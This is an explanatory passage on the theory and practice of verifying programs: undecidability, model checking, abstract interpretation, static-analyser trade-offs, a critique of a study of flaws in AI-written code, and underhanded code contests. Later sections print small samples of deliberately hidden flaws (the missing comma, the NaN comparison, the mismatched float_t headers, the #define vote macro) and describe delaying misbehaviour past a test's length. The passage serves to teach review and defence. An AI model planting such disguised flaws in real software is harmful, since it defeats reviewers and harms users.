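Melo and colleagues argued in 2025 that AI systems restricted to finite machines that always halt would escape the undecidability that Rice's theorem proves. In reply, Gumbau Mezquita (2026) argues in *The Unverifiability of Artificial General Intelligence (AGI) Alignment, Static and Dynamic* that finite hardware doesn't make certification possible.

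His argument uses a theorem about first-order logic, a language for making statements about objects and the relations between them. Boris Trakhtenbrot proved in 1950 that no algorithm can list exactly the first-order statements that are true in every finite structure. The proof again relies on the halting problem. For any machine $M$, we can write a statement that describes a complete run of $M$, from start to halt, on a grid of times and memory cells. Some finite grid fits the description if and only if $M$ halts. If $M$ runs forever, the statement's negation is true in every finite structure, so the supposed algorithm would eventually list it. That would confirm that $M$ runs forever, and no algorithm can confirm this for every such $M$.

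Gumbau Mezquita accepts that exhaustive search decides whether any one finite structure is safe, but his undecidability result is about all finite structures at once. For example, suppose the Goldbach program from the previous section stops when it runs out of memory. On a machine with $m$ bits, it can test even numbers only up to some limit, so a long enough search will determine whether it ever deletes anything on that machine. The same algorithm works for any given $m$. But showing that the program is safe for every $m$ would prove Goldbach's conjecture.

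A company knows, or can set, how much memory a script will have. It therefore needs a verdict for only one value of $m$, or a few values, which Trakhtenbrot's theorem doesn't rule out. Gumbau Mezquita wants a guarantee for all sizes because an AI that rewrites itself might move to any finite configuration. This matters only if the AI's memory has no cap, because a cap leaves finitely many possible configurations and makes the question decidable again.

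Gumbau Mezquita's argument about computing time is more relevant to a company with a fixed server. He says that checking even one finite system is PSPACE-hard in the worst case, which means it is at least as hard as every problem that a computer can solve with an amount of memory polynomial in the length of the input. Most complexity theorists expect that some of these problems have no polynomial-time algorithm, though nobody has proved it. He claims that, on this assumption, some specifications have no sub-exponential checking procedure. That doesn't follow, because an algorithm can be slower than every polynomial and still much faster than exponential. Theorem 3 doesn't depend on that assumption, but it concerns time budgets.

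### Unrolling loops

A test run covers one input. Bounded model checking covers all inputs together, but only for a limited number of passes through each loop. Consider this program:

```
# the input n is 1, 2 or 3
x = n
while x < 20:
    x = 2*x + 1
if x == 23:
    delete_everything()
```

*Software Verification with CPAchecker 3.0* (2024), a guide to a tool for analysing programs, describes the method in three steps. Applied to this example, they are:

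1. Choose a bound $k$ and replace the loop with $k$ copies of its body, each of which runs only if the loop's condition still holds. Take $k = 3$.
2. Translate the result into a logical formula that is true exactly when some input leads to a violation within the bound. Each successive value of `x` gets its own name. For runs that go round the loop three times, the formula requires all of the following:

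$$x_0 \in \{1,2,3\},\quad x_1 = 2x_0+1,\quad x_2 = 2x_1+1,\quad x_3 = 2x_2+1,$$
$$x_0, x_1, x_2 < 20,\quad x_3 = 23.$$

The full formula also allows for runs that leave the loop earlier. A program called a solver then looks for values that make the formula true. Here it finds $x_0 = 2$, $x_1 = 5$, $x_2 = 11$ and $x_3 = 23$.

The solver has found a witness: with the input 2, the program deletes everything.

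With $k = 2$ the solver would have found no violation, because `x` is at most 15 after two passes and every run is still in the loop, so the right verdict is "unknown". Suppose the last test were `x == 25` instead. With $k = 3$ there is no violation, but the run with input 1 has only reached `x` = 15 and is still in the loop, so the verdict is still "unknown". With $k = 4$ every run has left the loop without deleting anything, and the checker can declare the program safe for all three inputs. *Software Verification with CPAchecker 3.0* also describes a mode that starts with a bound of 0 and raises it by 1 until the tool reaches a verdict.

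A bounded checker therefore has to check whether it has unrolled a loop far enough. *CBMC* (2023) describes a bounded model checker for the programming language C that can add an "unwinding assertion", a check that no run would go round the loop again. In the paper's example, a binary search passes this check with a bound of 6 and fails it with any lower bound. If a loop has no upper limit, CBMC can still look for bugs, but it doesn't attempt to find them all.

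*Model Checking C Programs with Loops via k-Induction and Invariants* (2015) reports that bounded model checkers have found subtle bugs in real programs but typically fail to verify programs whose loops run an unknown number of times. A bounded model checker would return "unknown" for the Goldbach program at every bound that is practical to try.

### Comparing two versions of a program

If a program has a fixed input size and runs for a fixed number of steps, we can turn it into a Boolean circuit, a loop-free network of simple gates that combine bits. Checking whether a refactored function agrees with the old version on every input then means checking whether two circuits always give the same output. If the function takes two 32-bit numbers, there are $2^{64}$ possible inputs, so testing them all at a billion a second would take about 585 years.

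A solver can instead combine the two circuits into one that gives both the same input and outputs 1 if their results differ. The two versions are equivalent exactly when this combined circuit never outputs 1. Deciding whether a circuit can output 1 is the circuit satisfiability problem. Chapman and Williams point out in *Black-Box Hypotheses and Lower Bounds* (2021) that this problem is decidable, because a circuit has a finite table of outputs, but also NP-hard. NP is the class of problems whose "yes" answers have short witnesses that a machine can check quickly, and an NP-hard problem is at least as hard as every problem in that class.

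Comparing circuits is just as difficult, because we can find out whether a circuit can ever output 1 by comparing it with a circuit that always outputs 0. Circuit equivalence is therefore coNP-complete, which means it is among the hardest problems whose "no" answers have short witnesses. Here the witness is an input on which the two versions disagree, which proves that the refactoring changed the circuit's behaviour. If P and NP are different, as most researchers believe, no polynomial-time algorithm can compare every pair of circuits correctly. If NP and coNP also differ, then in any proof system whose proofs can be checked quickly, some equivalent pairs will have no short proof of equivalence.

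None of this shows that a particular comparison will be slow. The Exponential Time Hypothesis is a stronger assumption than $P \ne NP$, and *A Casual Tour Around a Circuit Complexity Bound* (2011) says a majority of researchers believe it. Under this hypothesis, satisfiability takes time $2^{\alpha n}$ for some constant $\alpha$ greater than 0, where $n$ is the number of variables. But $\alpha$ could be small. With $\alpha = 0.1$ and $n = 64$, $2^{\alpha n}$ is less than 100. The hypothesis describes how running time grows as problems get larger, and it puts no useful minimum on the time needed to compare two 64-bit functions.

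### Reading a circuit or only running it

Rice's theorem might suggest that a reviewer can learn nothing reliable from reading a program beyond what running it would show. Researchers have tried to state this idea exactly for circuits. The simplest version, that every non-trivial semantic property of circuits is hard to decide, is false. The property "outputs 0 when every input bit is 0" is a counterexample, because a reviewer can check it by running the circuit once on that input.

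*A Second Step Towards Complexity-Theoretic Analogs of Rice's Theorem* recounts that Borchert and Stephan responded by studying counting properties, which depend only on how many inputs make a circuit output 1. Later researchers proved a version of Rice's theorem for these properties, with NP-hardness in place of undecidability.

In *On the (Im)possibility of Obfuscating Programs* (2010), the full version of a 2001 conference paper, Barak, Goldreich and colleagues conjectured that if an efficient algorithm can decide a semantic property by reading a circuit, another efficient algorithm can decide it given only the circuit's size and the ability to run the circuit on inputs of its choice. They called this a scaled-down Rice's theorem.

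They then disproved a version in which the reviewer knows in advance that the circuit belongs to one of two groups and only has to say which. The disproof assumes, as much of cryptography does, that one-way functions exist, which are easy to compute but hard to reverse. The basic idea uses two programs. The first contains a secret key and a secret reply, and gives the reply only when its input is the key. The second takes the text of any program, runs that program on the key, and reports whether it gives the reply. Someone who has the text of the first program can feed it to the second and get a "yes", but someone who can only run the first program has no text to feed in and would have to guess the key.

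Barak and colleagues built a family of circuits that can be reconstructed quickly from any circuit that computes the same function, even though running them on chosen inputs doesn't reveal even one particular bit of the original. This rules out a general method of disguising programs so that reading the disguised version reveals no more than running it would. The researchers call their counterexample somewhat contrived and leave open weaker forms of disguise, which may be all that someone hiding a flaw needs.

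The original conjecture, which assumes no advance knowledge, is still unsettled. *Does Looking Inside a Circuit Help?* (Impagliazzo, Kabanets and colleagues, 2017) explains why it would be hard to prove. An algorithm that can only run a circuit with $n$ input bits needs about $2^n$ runs to tell whether it ever outputs 1. If reading the circuit didn't help, satisfiability would have no efficient algorithm, so a proof of the conjecture would also prove that P differs from NP. The paper also shows that certain kinds of counterexample would give surprisingly fast methods for satisfiability, so the conjecture may be hard to disprove too. Chapman and Williams proved versions of it for much weaker readers, such as circuits with a fixed number of layers. Those readers can't compute enough to learn anything useful from the code, so they are a poor model of a human reviewer or a modern analysis tool.

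### Tests on random programs

All these results concern the worst program a reviewer might receive. Pérez-Acle wanted to see how often a short test fails on programs that nobody designed to defeat it. He generated 2.2 million random programs for a simple simulated computer, 200,000 at each of eleven lengths from 4 to 24 instructions. He ran each for a fixed number of steps and recorded whether it performed a forbidden action. To label the programs correctly, he used evidence such as a program halting or returning to an earlier configuration, and excluded programs that none of his methods could settle.

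Of the programs, 1.6% were unsafe. An 8-step test missed none of the unsafe programs of length 4, but it missed 30.2% of those of length 24. At length 24, the share missed fell to 2.9% with a 16-step test and 0.2% with a 32-step test. Across the whole sample, a 64-step test missed two unsafe programs, and tests of 128 steps or more missed none. At every length, at least half of the unsafe programs broke the rule within six steps.

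Running the test for longer didn't eliminate its errors on the rule against leaking secrets. The test ran each program once for each secret and compared what it had published when time ran out. With 64 steps or more, the test wrongly rejected between 0.03% and 0.37% of the compliant programs, depending on program length, and this share didn't fall even at 4,096 steps. Pérez-Acle examined the 5,434 programs that the longest test wrongly rejected. Every one published the same endless sequence for both secrets, but at different speeds, so whenever the test stopped, one output was longer than the other. Comparing the outputs only up to the length of the shorter one would remove these false alarms, but it would also clear a program that leaks by publishing a value for one secret and nothing for the other.

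The results for the forbidden action suggest that long-delayed violations are rare among random programs, but the results are weak evidence about code that people or AI systems write. As Pérez-Acle says, a different way of choosing programs would give different error rates. His programs were short and contained no constant larger than 7, so few of them could count for long before acting. Excluding the unsettled programs may also have removed some of the hardest cases. The test for forbidden actions also used only one input, whereas the Steam script was dangerous only when a variable was empty. Running that script for a million steps with the variable set correctly would have missed the flaw.

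The results for random programs also don't cover an author who knows how long the test is and can delay the forbidden action until it ends. Pérez-Acle describes a program that counts down from a number $d$ and performs the forbidden action at step $2d + 3$. With $d = 10$, it acts at step 23, and a 32-step test catches it. Changing $d$ to 10,000 delays the action until step 20,003, past the end of every test he ran on the random programs.

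## How static analysers trade missed flaws against false alarms

Reviewers who can't rely on tests alone can turn to static analysis, which draws conclusions about a program's behaviour without running it. By Rice's theorem, every static analyser for clean-up scripts must lack at least one of three properties: always stopping, soundness (never clearing a script that can delete files outside its folder) and completeness (never flagging a script that can't).

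Some tools, such as bounded model checkers, can also answer "unknown", but the reviewer still has to either accept the script and risk missing a flaw or reject it and risk a false alarm. Rerunning a bounded model checker with ever higher bounds avoids both errors but may never end.

The common kinds of tool make different choices:

| Tool | What it usually gives up |
|---|---|
| Type checker | completeness |
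| Sound verifier | completeness |
| Bug finder | soundness, and some completeness |
| Compiler warnings | soundness and completeness |
| Model checker that keeps raising its bound | stopping on every program |

A type checker looks for operations on the wrong kind of value, such as adding 1 to a piece of text. In this program, `n` is a whole number:

```
if n * n < 0:
    total = "none"
else:
    total = 5
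print(total + 1)
```

The first branch never runs, so the addition always works. A typical sound type checker still rejects the program, because it doesn't work out which branches can run. Some language designers prefer to miss a few errors. *Type Unsoundness in Practice* (2016) explains that the designers of the programming language Dart deliberately gave it an unsound type system, partly to spare programmers many spurious warnings.

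Compilers, which translate source code into machine instructions, also warn about suspicious code. Programmers turn these checks off if they are slow or raise too many false alarms, so the checks mostly cover simple cases. For example, a compiler may warn about a line that writes to position −1 of an array but give no warning if the −1 comes from a calculation in another file.

### Abstract interpretation

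In 1977 Patrick Cousot and Radhia Cousot published abstract interpretation, a general method for building analysers that are sound and always stop. The analyser works through the program using descriptions of sets of values instead of individual values. Each description must cover every value a variable can have at that point in the program. It may also cover values the variable never has, which cause false alarms.

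An analyser could look for the Steam mistake in the clean-up script using just three descriptions of the setting `$CACHE_DIR`, which are "empty", "not empty" and "could be either". The setting could be either at the start, so the analyser flags the line that deletes files. If the script first checks the setting and exits when it is empty, the description at that line is "not empty", and the analyser no longer flags it.

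For numbers, the simplest useful description is an interval, written $[a,b]$ for everything from $a$ to $b$. To subtract one interval from another, the analyser takes the smallest and largest differences that the two ranges allow:

$$[a,b]-[c,d]=[a-d,\;b-c].$$

Suppose `x` is between 0 and 10, and the program divides 100 by `x - x + 1`. The rule gives $[0,10]-[0,10]=[-10,10]$ for `x - x`, and adding 1 gives $[-9,11]$. This interval contains 0, so the analyser warns of a possible division by zero. The divisor is always 1, but the interval rule allows for an impossible run in which the first `x` is 0 and the second is 10.

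The analyser could remove this alarm by simplifying `x - x` to 0 before it starts. That wouldn't help if the program first set `y = x` and then divided by `x - y + 1`. A more general solution is to record relations between variables, for instance by storing an upper limit on the difference between each pair. After `y = x`, the analyser stores

$$x-y\le 0 \quad\text{and}\quad y-x\le 0.$$

Together these show that `x - y` is 0, so the divisor is 1 and there is no alarm.

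This precision takes a lot of computation. A program with 10,000 variables needs 10,000 intervals but about 100 million limits on differences. The limits also affect each other. For example, if $x-y\le 2$ and $y-z\le 3$, then $x-z\le 5$. The standard way to find all such consequences is to go through every group of three variables, which takes about a trillion steps in this case. Analysers for large programs can reduce this work by tracking relations only within small groups of variables, but they may then miss a relation that would have removed an alarm.

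Even with these relations, false alarms remain. If `x` is a whole number from 0 to 10, the divisor `x*x - 4*x + 5` is never less than 1, because it equals $(x-2)^2+1$. Interval arithmetic gives $[0,100]-[0,40]+5=[-35,105]$, which includes zero, and limits on the differences between variables don't exclude it. Checking the eleven values of `x` separately would rule out zero, but ten such variables have about 26 billion combinations.

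### Making the analysis of a loop stop

Loops create another difficulty. This program fills an array of 1,000 elements, numbered 0 to 999, with zeros:

```
i = 0
while i < 1000:
    a[i] = 0
    i = i + 1
```

An interval analyser that follows the loop finds that `i` is in $[0,0]$ at the top of the loop, then $[0,1]$, then $[0,2]$, and needs a thousand rounds before the interval stops growing. If the loop had no upper limit, the analysis would never end. Widening solves this by replacing a limit that keeps moving with infinity:

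1. The analyser starts with $[0,0]$ at the top of the loop. After one pass the interval is $[0,1]$. The upper limit has moved, so the analyser widens the interval to $[0,\infty)$.
2. It analyses the loop again from $[0,\infty)$. The condition `i < 1000` reduces the interval inside the loop to $[0,999]$, and adding 1 gives $[1,1000]$.
3. Including the starting value 0, the new interval at the top is $[0,1000]$. This lies inside $[0,\infty)$, so the analyser has covered every run and can stop widening. It can also keep the tighter interval, a step known as narrowing.

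Inside the loop, `i` is between 0 and 999, so every write to the array is safe. The analysis finishes no matter how many times the loop runs, because it can move each end of an interval to infinity only once.

Widening can lose information that narrowing doesn't recover. If the condition is `i != 1000`, the program behaves the same way, but removing 1000 from the middle of $[0,\infty)$ doesn't leave an interval. The analyser has to keep $[0,\infty)$ inside the loop, so it warns that `a[i]` may be outside the array. A better widening rule first tries constants from the program as bounds. It would try $[0,1000]$, which the condition reduces to $[0,999]$, and the alarm would disappear.

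Designers can keep adding improvements of this kind without ever removing all the false alarms. But a company doesn't need precision on every program, so designers can choose improvements that suit the kind it writes.

### Astrée on flight-control code

The best-known success of this approach is Astrée, an analyser from the École Normale Supérieure in Paris. Mauborgne writes in *ASTRÉE* that the project began informally in December 2001, after Patrick Cousot claimed that specialising an analyser for a class of programs could make it both more precise and more efficient. The developers started with 10,000 lines of avionics code.

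ENS's *The Astrée Static Analyzer* reports that in November 2003, Astrée automatically proved that the primary flight-control software of the Airbus A340 had no run-time errors, such as dividing by zero or reading outside an array. The proof left no alarms for a person to examine. The program had 132,000 lines of C, and the analysis took 1 hour 20 minutes on an ordinary PC.

Flight-control code is unusually suitable for such an analysis. Feret (2013) describes programs that set up their variables and then repeat one cycle forever, reading inputs, computing, writing outputs and waiting for the next clock tick. The proof covers every cycle. The programs don't request extra memory while running, and no function calls itself. They are still hard to analyse, with more than 100,000 lines, more than 10,000 variables and a lot of floating-point arithmetic.

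Airbus needed close to zero false alarms. If an analyser flagged 5% of the lines in the A340 program, one person would need more than three years to examine the 6,600 alarms at an hour each. Souyris and Delmas write in *Experimental Assessment of Astrée on Safety-Critical Avionics Software* that Astrée at first produced few false alarms, but Airbus still had to reduce them to zero for safety and industrial reasons. The two Airbus engineers write elsewhere that specialising the tool takes two stages, in which its developers design it for a family of programs and the user then tunes it for each program (Delmas and Souyris).

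According to Kastner (2010), reaching zero false alarms also requires annotations, which give the analyser facts it can't work out from the code. If an annotation gives a maximum sensor reading and the real sensor exceeds it, the proof no longer applies to the aircraft. Software can also be free of run-time errors and still steer the aircraft incorrectly.

Outside this family of programs, the results are less impressive. A successor, AstréeA, was designed for avionics software in which several tasks run asynchronously. After four years it could analyse a program of 1.6 million lines, "albeit with many alarms", according to *INS*, a project description from the French national research agency (ANR). *Of compiler warnings discussions* (2013), from the makers of Frama-C, another analyser for C, reports plenty of false positives and one extremely minor real issue in an analysis of zlib, a widely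 used compression library, that was still under way.

### Language features that analysers ignore

Most business software uses features that flight-control code avoids. JavaScript's `eval`, for example, runs a piece of text as code, and shell scripts have an `eval` command too. If the clean-up script contains `eval "$STEP"`, and `$STEP` comes from a settings file, the line could run any command. A sound analyser would have to flag the script unless it could work out what the file contains.

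Livshits et al. (2015, *In Defense of Soundiness*) say they know of no realistic whole-program analyser that doesn't make unsound choices on purpose. For example, an analyser may treat `eval` as doing nothing unless it can work out in advance what text `eval` will run. Many analysers for C and C++ ignore certain conversions between numbers and memory addresses. Their claim excludes modular analyses such as type systems, which don't need to model all the data that the parts of a program share. Astrée seems to be an exception, but it was designed for programs that avoid many of the features that are hardest to analyse.

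"In Defense of Soundiness: A Manifesto" calls an analysis "soundy" if it covers every behaviour of most language features but deliberately ignores some behaviours of a few features that experts know well. The paper distinguishes this from arbitrary shortcuts and recommends that developers state what each analysis leaves out. Otherwise, someone who reads only that a tool is sound may assume that the guarantee covers their program.

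Reflection lets a Java program choose by name, as it runs, which piece of code to use. *Defensive Points-To Analysis* reports that reflection puts about 80% of the programs in a collection of 461 outside the published soundness proofs. Livshits and his co-authors say that an analysis of Eclipse, a large programming environment, would probably omit most of the program if it ignored reflection.

Undecidability doesn't force developers to make these omissions. According to the statement, analysers could in principle handle every feature soundly by assuming that the difficult ones might do anything. But the results would then be too imprecise to be useful, and the analysis would often be too large to finish in reasonable time. By Rice's theorem, a sound analyser that always terminates must raise some false alarms, but developers decide how many to tolerate.

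Ignoring `eval` may be a reasonable compromise when an analyser is looking for accidental errors, but it is much riskier when flaws may be hidden deliberately, because an author can use a list of ignored features to choose where to hide a flaw.

### Why bug finders miss flaws on purpose

People who build bug finders have a practical reason to accept some missed flaws in exchange for fewer false alarms. If a checker raises too many, developers may get tired of it and switch it off, and then it catches nothing. Suppose a codebase requests memory in 1,000 places, and an attacker could exploit five of them. A checker that flags all 1,000 catches every flaw, but developers must read 200 alarms for each real one. A checker that flags only 20 places, including four of the flaws, misses one flaw, but developers read only five alarms for each one it finds.

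Clang, a compiler for C and related languages, includes a static analyser. C programs request memory with `malloc`, and often call `malloc(n * sizeof(int))` to get space for `n` whole numbers. If `n` is large enough, the multiplication overflows, meaning the result doesn't fit in the available bits and wraps round to a small number. The program then gets too little memory and may write past the end of it. *Alpha Checkers*, from LLVM, the project that develops Clang, shows a checker called MallocOverflow flagging this line.

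The developers deleted that checker in August 2024. Nagy (2024), in *[analyzer] Delete alpha.security.MallocOverflow*, calls it "too noisy to be useful right now". The checker used crude rules, such as assuming that a variable was probably not too large if the program had compared it with something. Nagy doubted that even a perfect version would be useful, because assuming by default that the size can overflow produces too many false alarms. Another developer, vabridgers (2024), supported the deletion and reported seeing so many false alarms that programmers disabled the checker.

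A newer Clang checker, which users have to switch on, warns about a memory request only if an attacker can control its size and the analyser can't prove that the size is below a generous limit (LLVM). *Overflow in uncontrolled allocation size* describes a similar query in CodeQL, GitHub's analysis tool. The query flags the multiplication when `n` comes from user input with no apparent guard on its size.

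Even tools designed to limit noise can produce many false alarms on AI-written code. AppSecSanta (2026) ran five open-source tools on 534 samples from six language models and confirmed 175 of their 1,173 findings, or about 15%. One person did the study, so no one independently checked which findings were real. The study also doesn't show how many flaws all five tools missed.

### "Broken by Default"

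In the April 2026 preprint *Broken by Default*, Blain and Noiseux (2026) claim that analysers miss almost all of one important group of flaws in AI-written code. They gave 500 programming tasks to seven language models and collected 3,500 code samples. There were 100 tasks each on memory allocation, integer arithmetic, authentication, cryptography and input handling. A typical task was to write a C function that reads `n` integers from a file and returns them as an array. The models included GPT-4o, Claude Haiku 4.5 and Gemini 2.5 Flash, so the sample doesn't represent the strongest models available at the time.

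The two researchers, who founded Cobalt AI, analysed the samples with their own tool, COBALT. It searches the code for suspicious patterns, such as a multiplication inside `malloc` with no check on its size. It then writes a formula describing the dangerous condition and passes it to Z3, a solver of the kind that bounded model checkers use. If Z3 finds values that make the formula true, the researchers count the flaw as formally proven exploitable.

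COBALT reported at least one flaw in 55.8% of the samples, with rates from 48.4% for Gemini 2.5 Flash to 62.4% for GPT-4o. The rate was highest for integer arithmetic, at 87%, and lowest for cryptography, at 25%. A solver proved 1,055 findings. In a smaller experiment with 50 tasks and five models, asking for secure code reduced the share of flawed samples only from 64.8% to 60.8%, and the memory-allocation flaws hardly changed.

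The researchers compared COBALT with six other tools on the 250 samples from that smaller set. COBALT had flagged 162 of them, 90 with solver proofs. They report that the six other tools together flagged 7.6% of the samples and missed 97.8% of the solver-proven flaws.

The second figure means that the tools missed 88 of 90. They flagged the other two only because the code also contained a risky text-copying command. The first figure is misleading because it counts only the 19 samples flagged by two of the six tools, Semgrep and Bandit. Three others (Cppcheck, Clang's analyser and FlawFinder) ran only on the 87 samples in C, where FlawFinder flagged four and the other two flagged none. CodeQL ran only on the 90 samples with solver proofs and flagged none. The paper therefore doesn't show what share of the 250 samples all six would have flagged together.

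Finally, the researchers gave each model code it had written that a solver had proven flawed, and asked it to look for security problems. The models identified 70 of 89 samples (78.7%) as vulnerable, ranging from 12 of 18 for GPT-4o to 17 of 17 for Mistral Large. Blain and Noiseux conclude that the models contain knowledge of these flaws but don't apply it when writing code. But the test included no safe code, so a model that called every sample vulnerable would have scored 100%. The results show that the models often recognise these flaws when asked, but not how many false alarms they would raise.

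### What the solver proved

For the memory request, Blain and Noiseux describe a formula in which `n` can be any 32-bit number and the multiplication wraps round at $2^{32}$. The solver looks for an `n` that satisfies

$$n \times \texttt{sizeof}(T) < n,$$

where $\texttt{sizeof}(T)$ is the size of one array element in bytes. For 4-byte elements, one answer is $n=2^{30}+1$. The true product is $2^{32}+4$, which wraps round to 4, so the program requests 4 bytes to store about a billion numbers.

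This is a correct proof about the multiplication, but the formula contains nothing else from the program. It doesn't show that `n` can ever have this value, or that an attacker can choose it. For 4-byte elements the formula is the same in every sample, so the solver always finds an answer. COBALT's first step, the search for a pattern without a guard, separates "proven" samples from clean ones, so the proof adds little to the pattern match.

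The formula also assumes 32-bit arithmetic. On an ordinary 64-bit machine, C does this multiplication with 64-bit numbers, so the same `n` produces a request for just over 4 gigabytes and doesn't wrap round. A much larger `n` could still overflow if the program stores it in 64 bits. Of the 90 solver-proven samples, 22 are in Python, whose ordinary integers don't overflow. The paper gives no formula for those samples.

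A solver can take much more of a program into account. *From TinyGo to gc Compiler* (2026) describes Zorya, a tool that follows a program's execution and records how each value depends on the input. The paper applies it to a function that calculates the fee for using memory in Go-Ethereum, software for the Ethereum network. The function guards against one overflow, but a later line squares a number and can still overflow. Zorya passes the solver the expressions collected up to that line to check whether the square can exceed 64 bits. In 0.39 seconds, the solver found an input that causes the overflow.

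Blain and Noiseux chose seven of their 1,055 findings, wrote programs to exploit them, and succeeded with six. Four of the six were memory errors, including a request for too much memory. The other two were a cracked password hash and a database attack, although the paper's abstract describes all six as crashes. The tests show that some of the flaws can cause real damage when the program receives the dangerous value, but seven chosen examples can't show how many of the findings are exploitable in practice.

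### Undecidability or design

Blain and Noiseux say that the other tools missed the overflow because neither pattern matching nor following a program's paths can detect it, and that this "is not a configuration issue". But Clang's deleted checker flagged the same line by matching patterns. The research tool *Arbiter* detects integer overflows in compiled programs by running a fast, imprecise static search and then a slower step that filters out false alarms.

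The researchers ran Semgrep with all its rules and Cppcheck with its most exhaustive options, but excluded low-severity findings from Bandit and FlawFinder. They give no version or settings for Clang's analyser. Its experimental checkers, which once included MallocOverflow, are off by default (LLVM's *Available Checkers*). CodeQL's query set included one for this overflow, but that query checks for sizes that come from user input and isn't designed to report anything if `n` is simply a parameter of the function.

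The comparison also favours COBALT because it uses COBALT's own findings as the list of real flaws. COBALT can't miss a flaw on that list, and the paper doesn't measure how many of those findings are false alarms. A tool that flagged every call to `malloc` would have caught all the allocation overflows.

Undecidability explains very little of the gap. Whether one 32-bit multiplication can overflow is decidable, and a solver can settle it almost at once. Whether `n` can reach a dangerous value in a complete program is undecidable in general. COBALT assumes that `n` can take any value, which risks false alarms, while CodeQL reports a problem only if it can trace `n` to user input, which risks missing flaws. Rice's theorem implies that neither policy can be right about every program, but it doesn't determine which policy a developer chooses or how often that policy fails on ordinary code.

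The paper doesn't give enough information to tell how many of the 88 missed findings were real flaws. Blain and Noiseux have published their data, so someone could trace where `n` comes from in each sample. If a sample is a single function without a surrounding program, whether the finding is a real flaw depends on the function's specification. If the function must be safe for every `n`, a missing guard is a flaw and CodeQL missed it. If the caller is responsible for keeping `n` small, the function is correct and COBALT raised a false alarm.

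## Underhanded code contests and what human reviewers miss

A human reviewer may notice a flaw that a static analyser misses, but a series of contests that began in 2004 has shown how easily reviewers can miss flaws too. Entrants write underhanded code, which is readable source code that looks correct but is designed to misbehave. The organisers publish the winning programs and explain the trick in each one, which real attackers rarely do.

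### The contests and their rules

In 2004, Daniel Horn started the Obfuscated V Contest, the earliest contest of this kind that Wheeler found. Entrants wrote programs in C or C++ that seemed to count votes correctly but gave wrong totals. Some of the programs miscounted only on Election Day, so they would have given correct totals in a test on any other date.

Horn's contest inspired the Underhanded C Contest, which Scott Craver first organised at Binghamton University. It ran from 2005 to 2009 and again from 2013 to 2015, with a new task each time.

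Contests in more specialised fields followed. The Underhanded Crypto Contest ran from 2014 to 2018, and the first Underhanded Solidity Coding Contest took place in 2017. Solidity is a language for smart contracts, which are programs that hold and transfer money on a blockchain such as Ethereum. Many entrants named a variable after a built-in feature, such as `now`, which normally gives the current time. A reader who knows the language will assume the usual meaning. Solidity's developers had added a warning about reusing built-in names shortly before the contest, and they used the entries to improve the language and its compiler further.

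*Results of the 2015 Underhanded C Contest* (Craver, 2016) lists what earned points in the final year. Short, readable programs scored higher because it is harder to hide a flaw in them. A flaw based on mistaking the letter l for the digit 1 was worth as much as one based on an obscure technical error. Programs also scored higher if they still looked innocent in an editor that colours different parts of the code, and if the flaw, once found, could pass for an honest mistake. The flaw had to be easy for a cheat to trigger but unlikely to be triggered by accident, so ordinary tests are also unlikely to trigger it.

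### A missing comma

Entrants in the Underhanded C Contest's *The 2009 challenge* (2009) had to write a program that reads an airline's luggage records and prints the current ones. A disgruntled check-in clerk could not alter a record but could add a comment to it. The program had to misroute a bag if the clerk wrote the right comment.

Sam Blackburn won with a 99-line program that replaces rude words in the comments. His list of words and replacements ends like this:

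```
"damn", "d*mn"
"bitch", "b*tch"
```

The first line should end with a comma. C joins adjacent pieces of quoted text, so the program replaces "damn" with the nine characters `d*mnbitch`. The extra text runs past the end of the comment and into the next field, which marks the record as deleted. The program then leaves that bag out of its output.

A simple textual check that requires a comma between adjacent quoted strings in a list would expose this flaw. A test with one comment for each word on the list would also expose it, because the record containing "damn" would vanish. A tool that watches for writes outside a program's blocks of memory would probably miss it, because the comment and the deletion mark are in the same block.

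One runner-up, only 71 lines long, drops a record if the comment begins with the digit zero, as in "0ffered passenger compensation". The author typed `'0'`, the digit, where the program needed `'\0'`, which marks the end of a piece of text.

### One name with two meanings

The 2015 task was based on a problem in nuclear disarmament. Inspectors want to confirm that a warhead contains plutonium, but the country that owns it doesn't want them to see its design. A program therefore compares a scan of the warhead with a trusted reference scan and reports only whether they match. Entrants had to write a comparison that the country under inspection could fool.

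Linus Åkesson won with about 60 lines of code. His program stores each number in a scan in 8 bytes, then passes the numbers to a function in another file that is written for 4-byte numbers. Both files call the number type `float_t`. The first file takes the definition from Åkesson's own header (a file of shared definitions), where it means an 8-byte number. The second takes it from C's standard mathematics header, where by default it means a 4-byte number. Neither file includes both headers, so the compiler never processes the two definitions together.

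The comparison function therefore reads each number as two numbers, and stops halfway through the scan. The scan's counts are whole numbers, and when a count is below about a million, one of the two numbers is zero. The other grows very slowly with the original count. A count of 10 becomes about 2.56 and a count of 1,000 about 4.48, so a hundredfold difference shrinks to less than twofold.

A country could remove most of the plutonium and add another material that shows up only in the second half of the scan. This material would let the scan pass an earlier check on its total energy, and the comparison would then ignore it. The small amount of plutonium left would look much like the full amount.

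Wheeler's list of possible countermeasures includes a ban on reusing the names of common library features, which would flag the line that defines `float_t`. Another remedy is requiring each file to include the header that declares its functions. The compiler would then find both definitions of `float_t` in one file and stop with an error. Even a careful reviewer who read only the comparison function would see a standard calculation with no errors.

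About a third of the 2015 entries used a different trick. Dividing zero by zero gives a special value called NaN, short for "not a number", and a comparison such as "NaN is less than 5" is always false. Suppose a program ends with this line, where 0 means "no match" and 1 means "match":

```
return (score < threshold ? 0 : 1);
```

A reader will probably take this to mean that the program accepts a warhead only if its score reaches the threshold. But a NaN score isn't less than the threshold, so the program accepts the warhead. The line `score >= threshold ? 1 : 0` would reject it, though the two lines give the same answer for every ordinary number.

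Readers can miss a flaw even when they know there is one. In the Underhanded C Contest's *Review of the 2014 Challenge* (2014), the organiser describes staring at a very short entry by Domenico Andreoli without finding the bug. The task was to write a program that archives messages for government surveillance but secretly lets users discover that they are being watched. The flaw was in a function that Andreoli described in a comment but left out of the code. The function downloads the user's profile picture from a web address, and a user who can observe requests to that address will know about the surveillance.

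### Wheeler's study of forty vote counters

Wheeler studied whether simple checks could catch underhanded code, in work for the Institute for Defense Analyses, a nonprofit that runs research centres for the US government. He went through the published entries to the 2004 vote-counting contest and identified the lines responsible for each attack. He excluded one program that contained no attack, leaving 40, two of them his own.

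Of the 40 programs, 25 used one of five kinds of mistake that programmers also make by accident. Nine misused `#define`, which tells the compiler to replace a name with other text, seven relied on confusing l with 1 or O with 0, and five read or wrote outside the intended memory. Two hid working code inside what looked like a comment, and two used `=`, which changes a value, in place of `==`, which compares two values.

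The `#define` attacks can be hard to see because the replacement is purely textual. One entrant defined "a vote for somebody else" like this:

```
#define OTHER(v) !BUSH(v) && !KERRY(v) && !NADER(v)
```

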